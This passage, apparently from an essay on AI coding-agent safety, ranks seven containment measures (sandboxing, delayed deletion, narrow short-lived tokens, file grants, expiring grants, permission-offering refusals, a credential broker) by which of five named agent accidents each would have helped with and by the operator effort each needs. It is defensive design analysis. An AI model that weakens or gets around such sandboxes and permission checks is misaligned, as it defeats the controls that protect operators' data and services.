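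The changes remove more steps from the checkout test. Today it takes her ten: she cancels two old tokens, replaces the live payment key and database password, creates three test credentials, opens two network addresses and later deletes the hosting token. With the changes, she approves a one-day test credential at each of three services. The old secrets can stay where they are if the sandbox hides them.

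These counts are for an invented shop, and making fewer decisions doesn't always save time. In Yan's experiment, writing rules reduced the number of prompts from 18 to about 11 but didn't reliably shorten the total time.

### Which changes to make first

One way to rank the changes is by which of five accidents each would probably have prevented or made reversible, and by how many decisions each would require from the operator. The five are the deleted home folder that Docker describes and the incidents involving PocketOS, DataTalks.Club, the July database and the September mirror.

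| Rank | Change | Accidents it would probably have helped with | Operator's decisions |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Sandbox on from installation, home folder hidden | Home folder; PocketOS, if Railway's address was closed | None |
| 2 | Delayed deletion at services | PocketOS; DataTalks.Club, if the delay covered snapshots | None |
| 3 | Short-lived, narrow tokens | PocketOS; July database; perhaps DataTalks.Club | One per service |
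| 4 | Files granted by choosing them | Home folder; September mirror, if the live project stayed read-only | One per file or folder |
| 5 | Grants that expire with the task | None clearly | None, unless a job resumes |
| 6 | Refusals that offer one permission | None directly | One per offer |
| 7 | Built-in broker | None by itself | A few at set-up |

The sandbox and delayed deletion require no effort from the operator in normal use, so they are ranked by the harm they prevent. The sandbox comes first because, for a job like the delivery fee, it blocks all three powers that could close the shop: the hosting token, the payment key and the email account. Delayed deletion covers only part of the danger from the hosting token, but it still works after someone has opened the network or switched the sandbox off. A hosting company can also introduce it without waiting for any agent maker.

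Narrow tokens might have helped with more of the five accidents than either the sandbox or file choice, but they require the user to make a decision at every service and each company to redesign its permissions. File choice, where the user picks which files the agent can open, comes next after the sandbox because it limits damage on the laptop with almost no extra effort. It depends on the sandbox, since without one the agent could open files the user didn't pick.

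The lower rankings are less certain. Expiring grants take little effort and prevent an old permission from causing a later accident, but none of the five accidents clearly involved a leftover grant in the harness. The token at PocketOS was a leftover, but Railway would have had to make it expire. Specific refusals rank sixth because they require users to make the most decisions, and the participants in Yan's experiment often decided badly. Agent makers should still build them together with the sandbox. Many Claude Code users have already loosened their permission checks, and a sandbox that only refuses would lead more people to do the same.

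The broker ranks last because a stolen token is of little use if it expires within a day and gives access only to a test site. If a service offers only permanent tokens that cover the whole account, the broker should rank much higher, because it would at least keep such a token out of files the agent can read.
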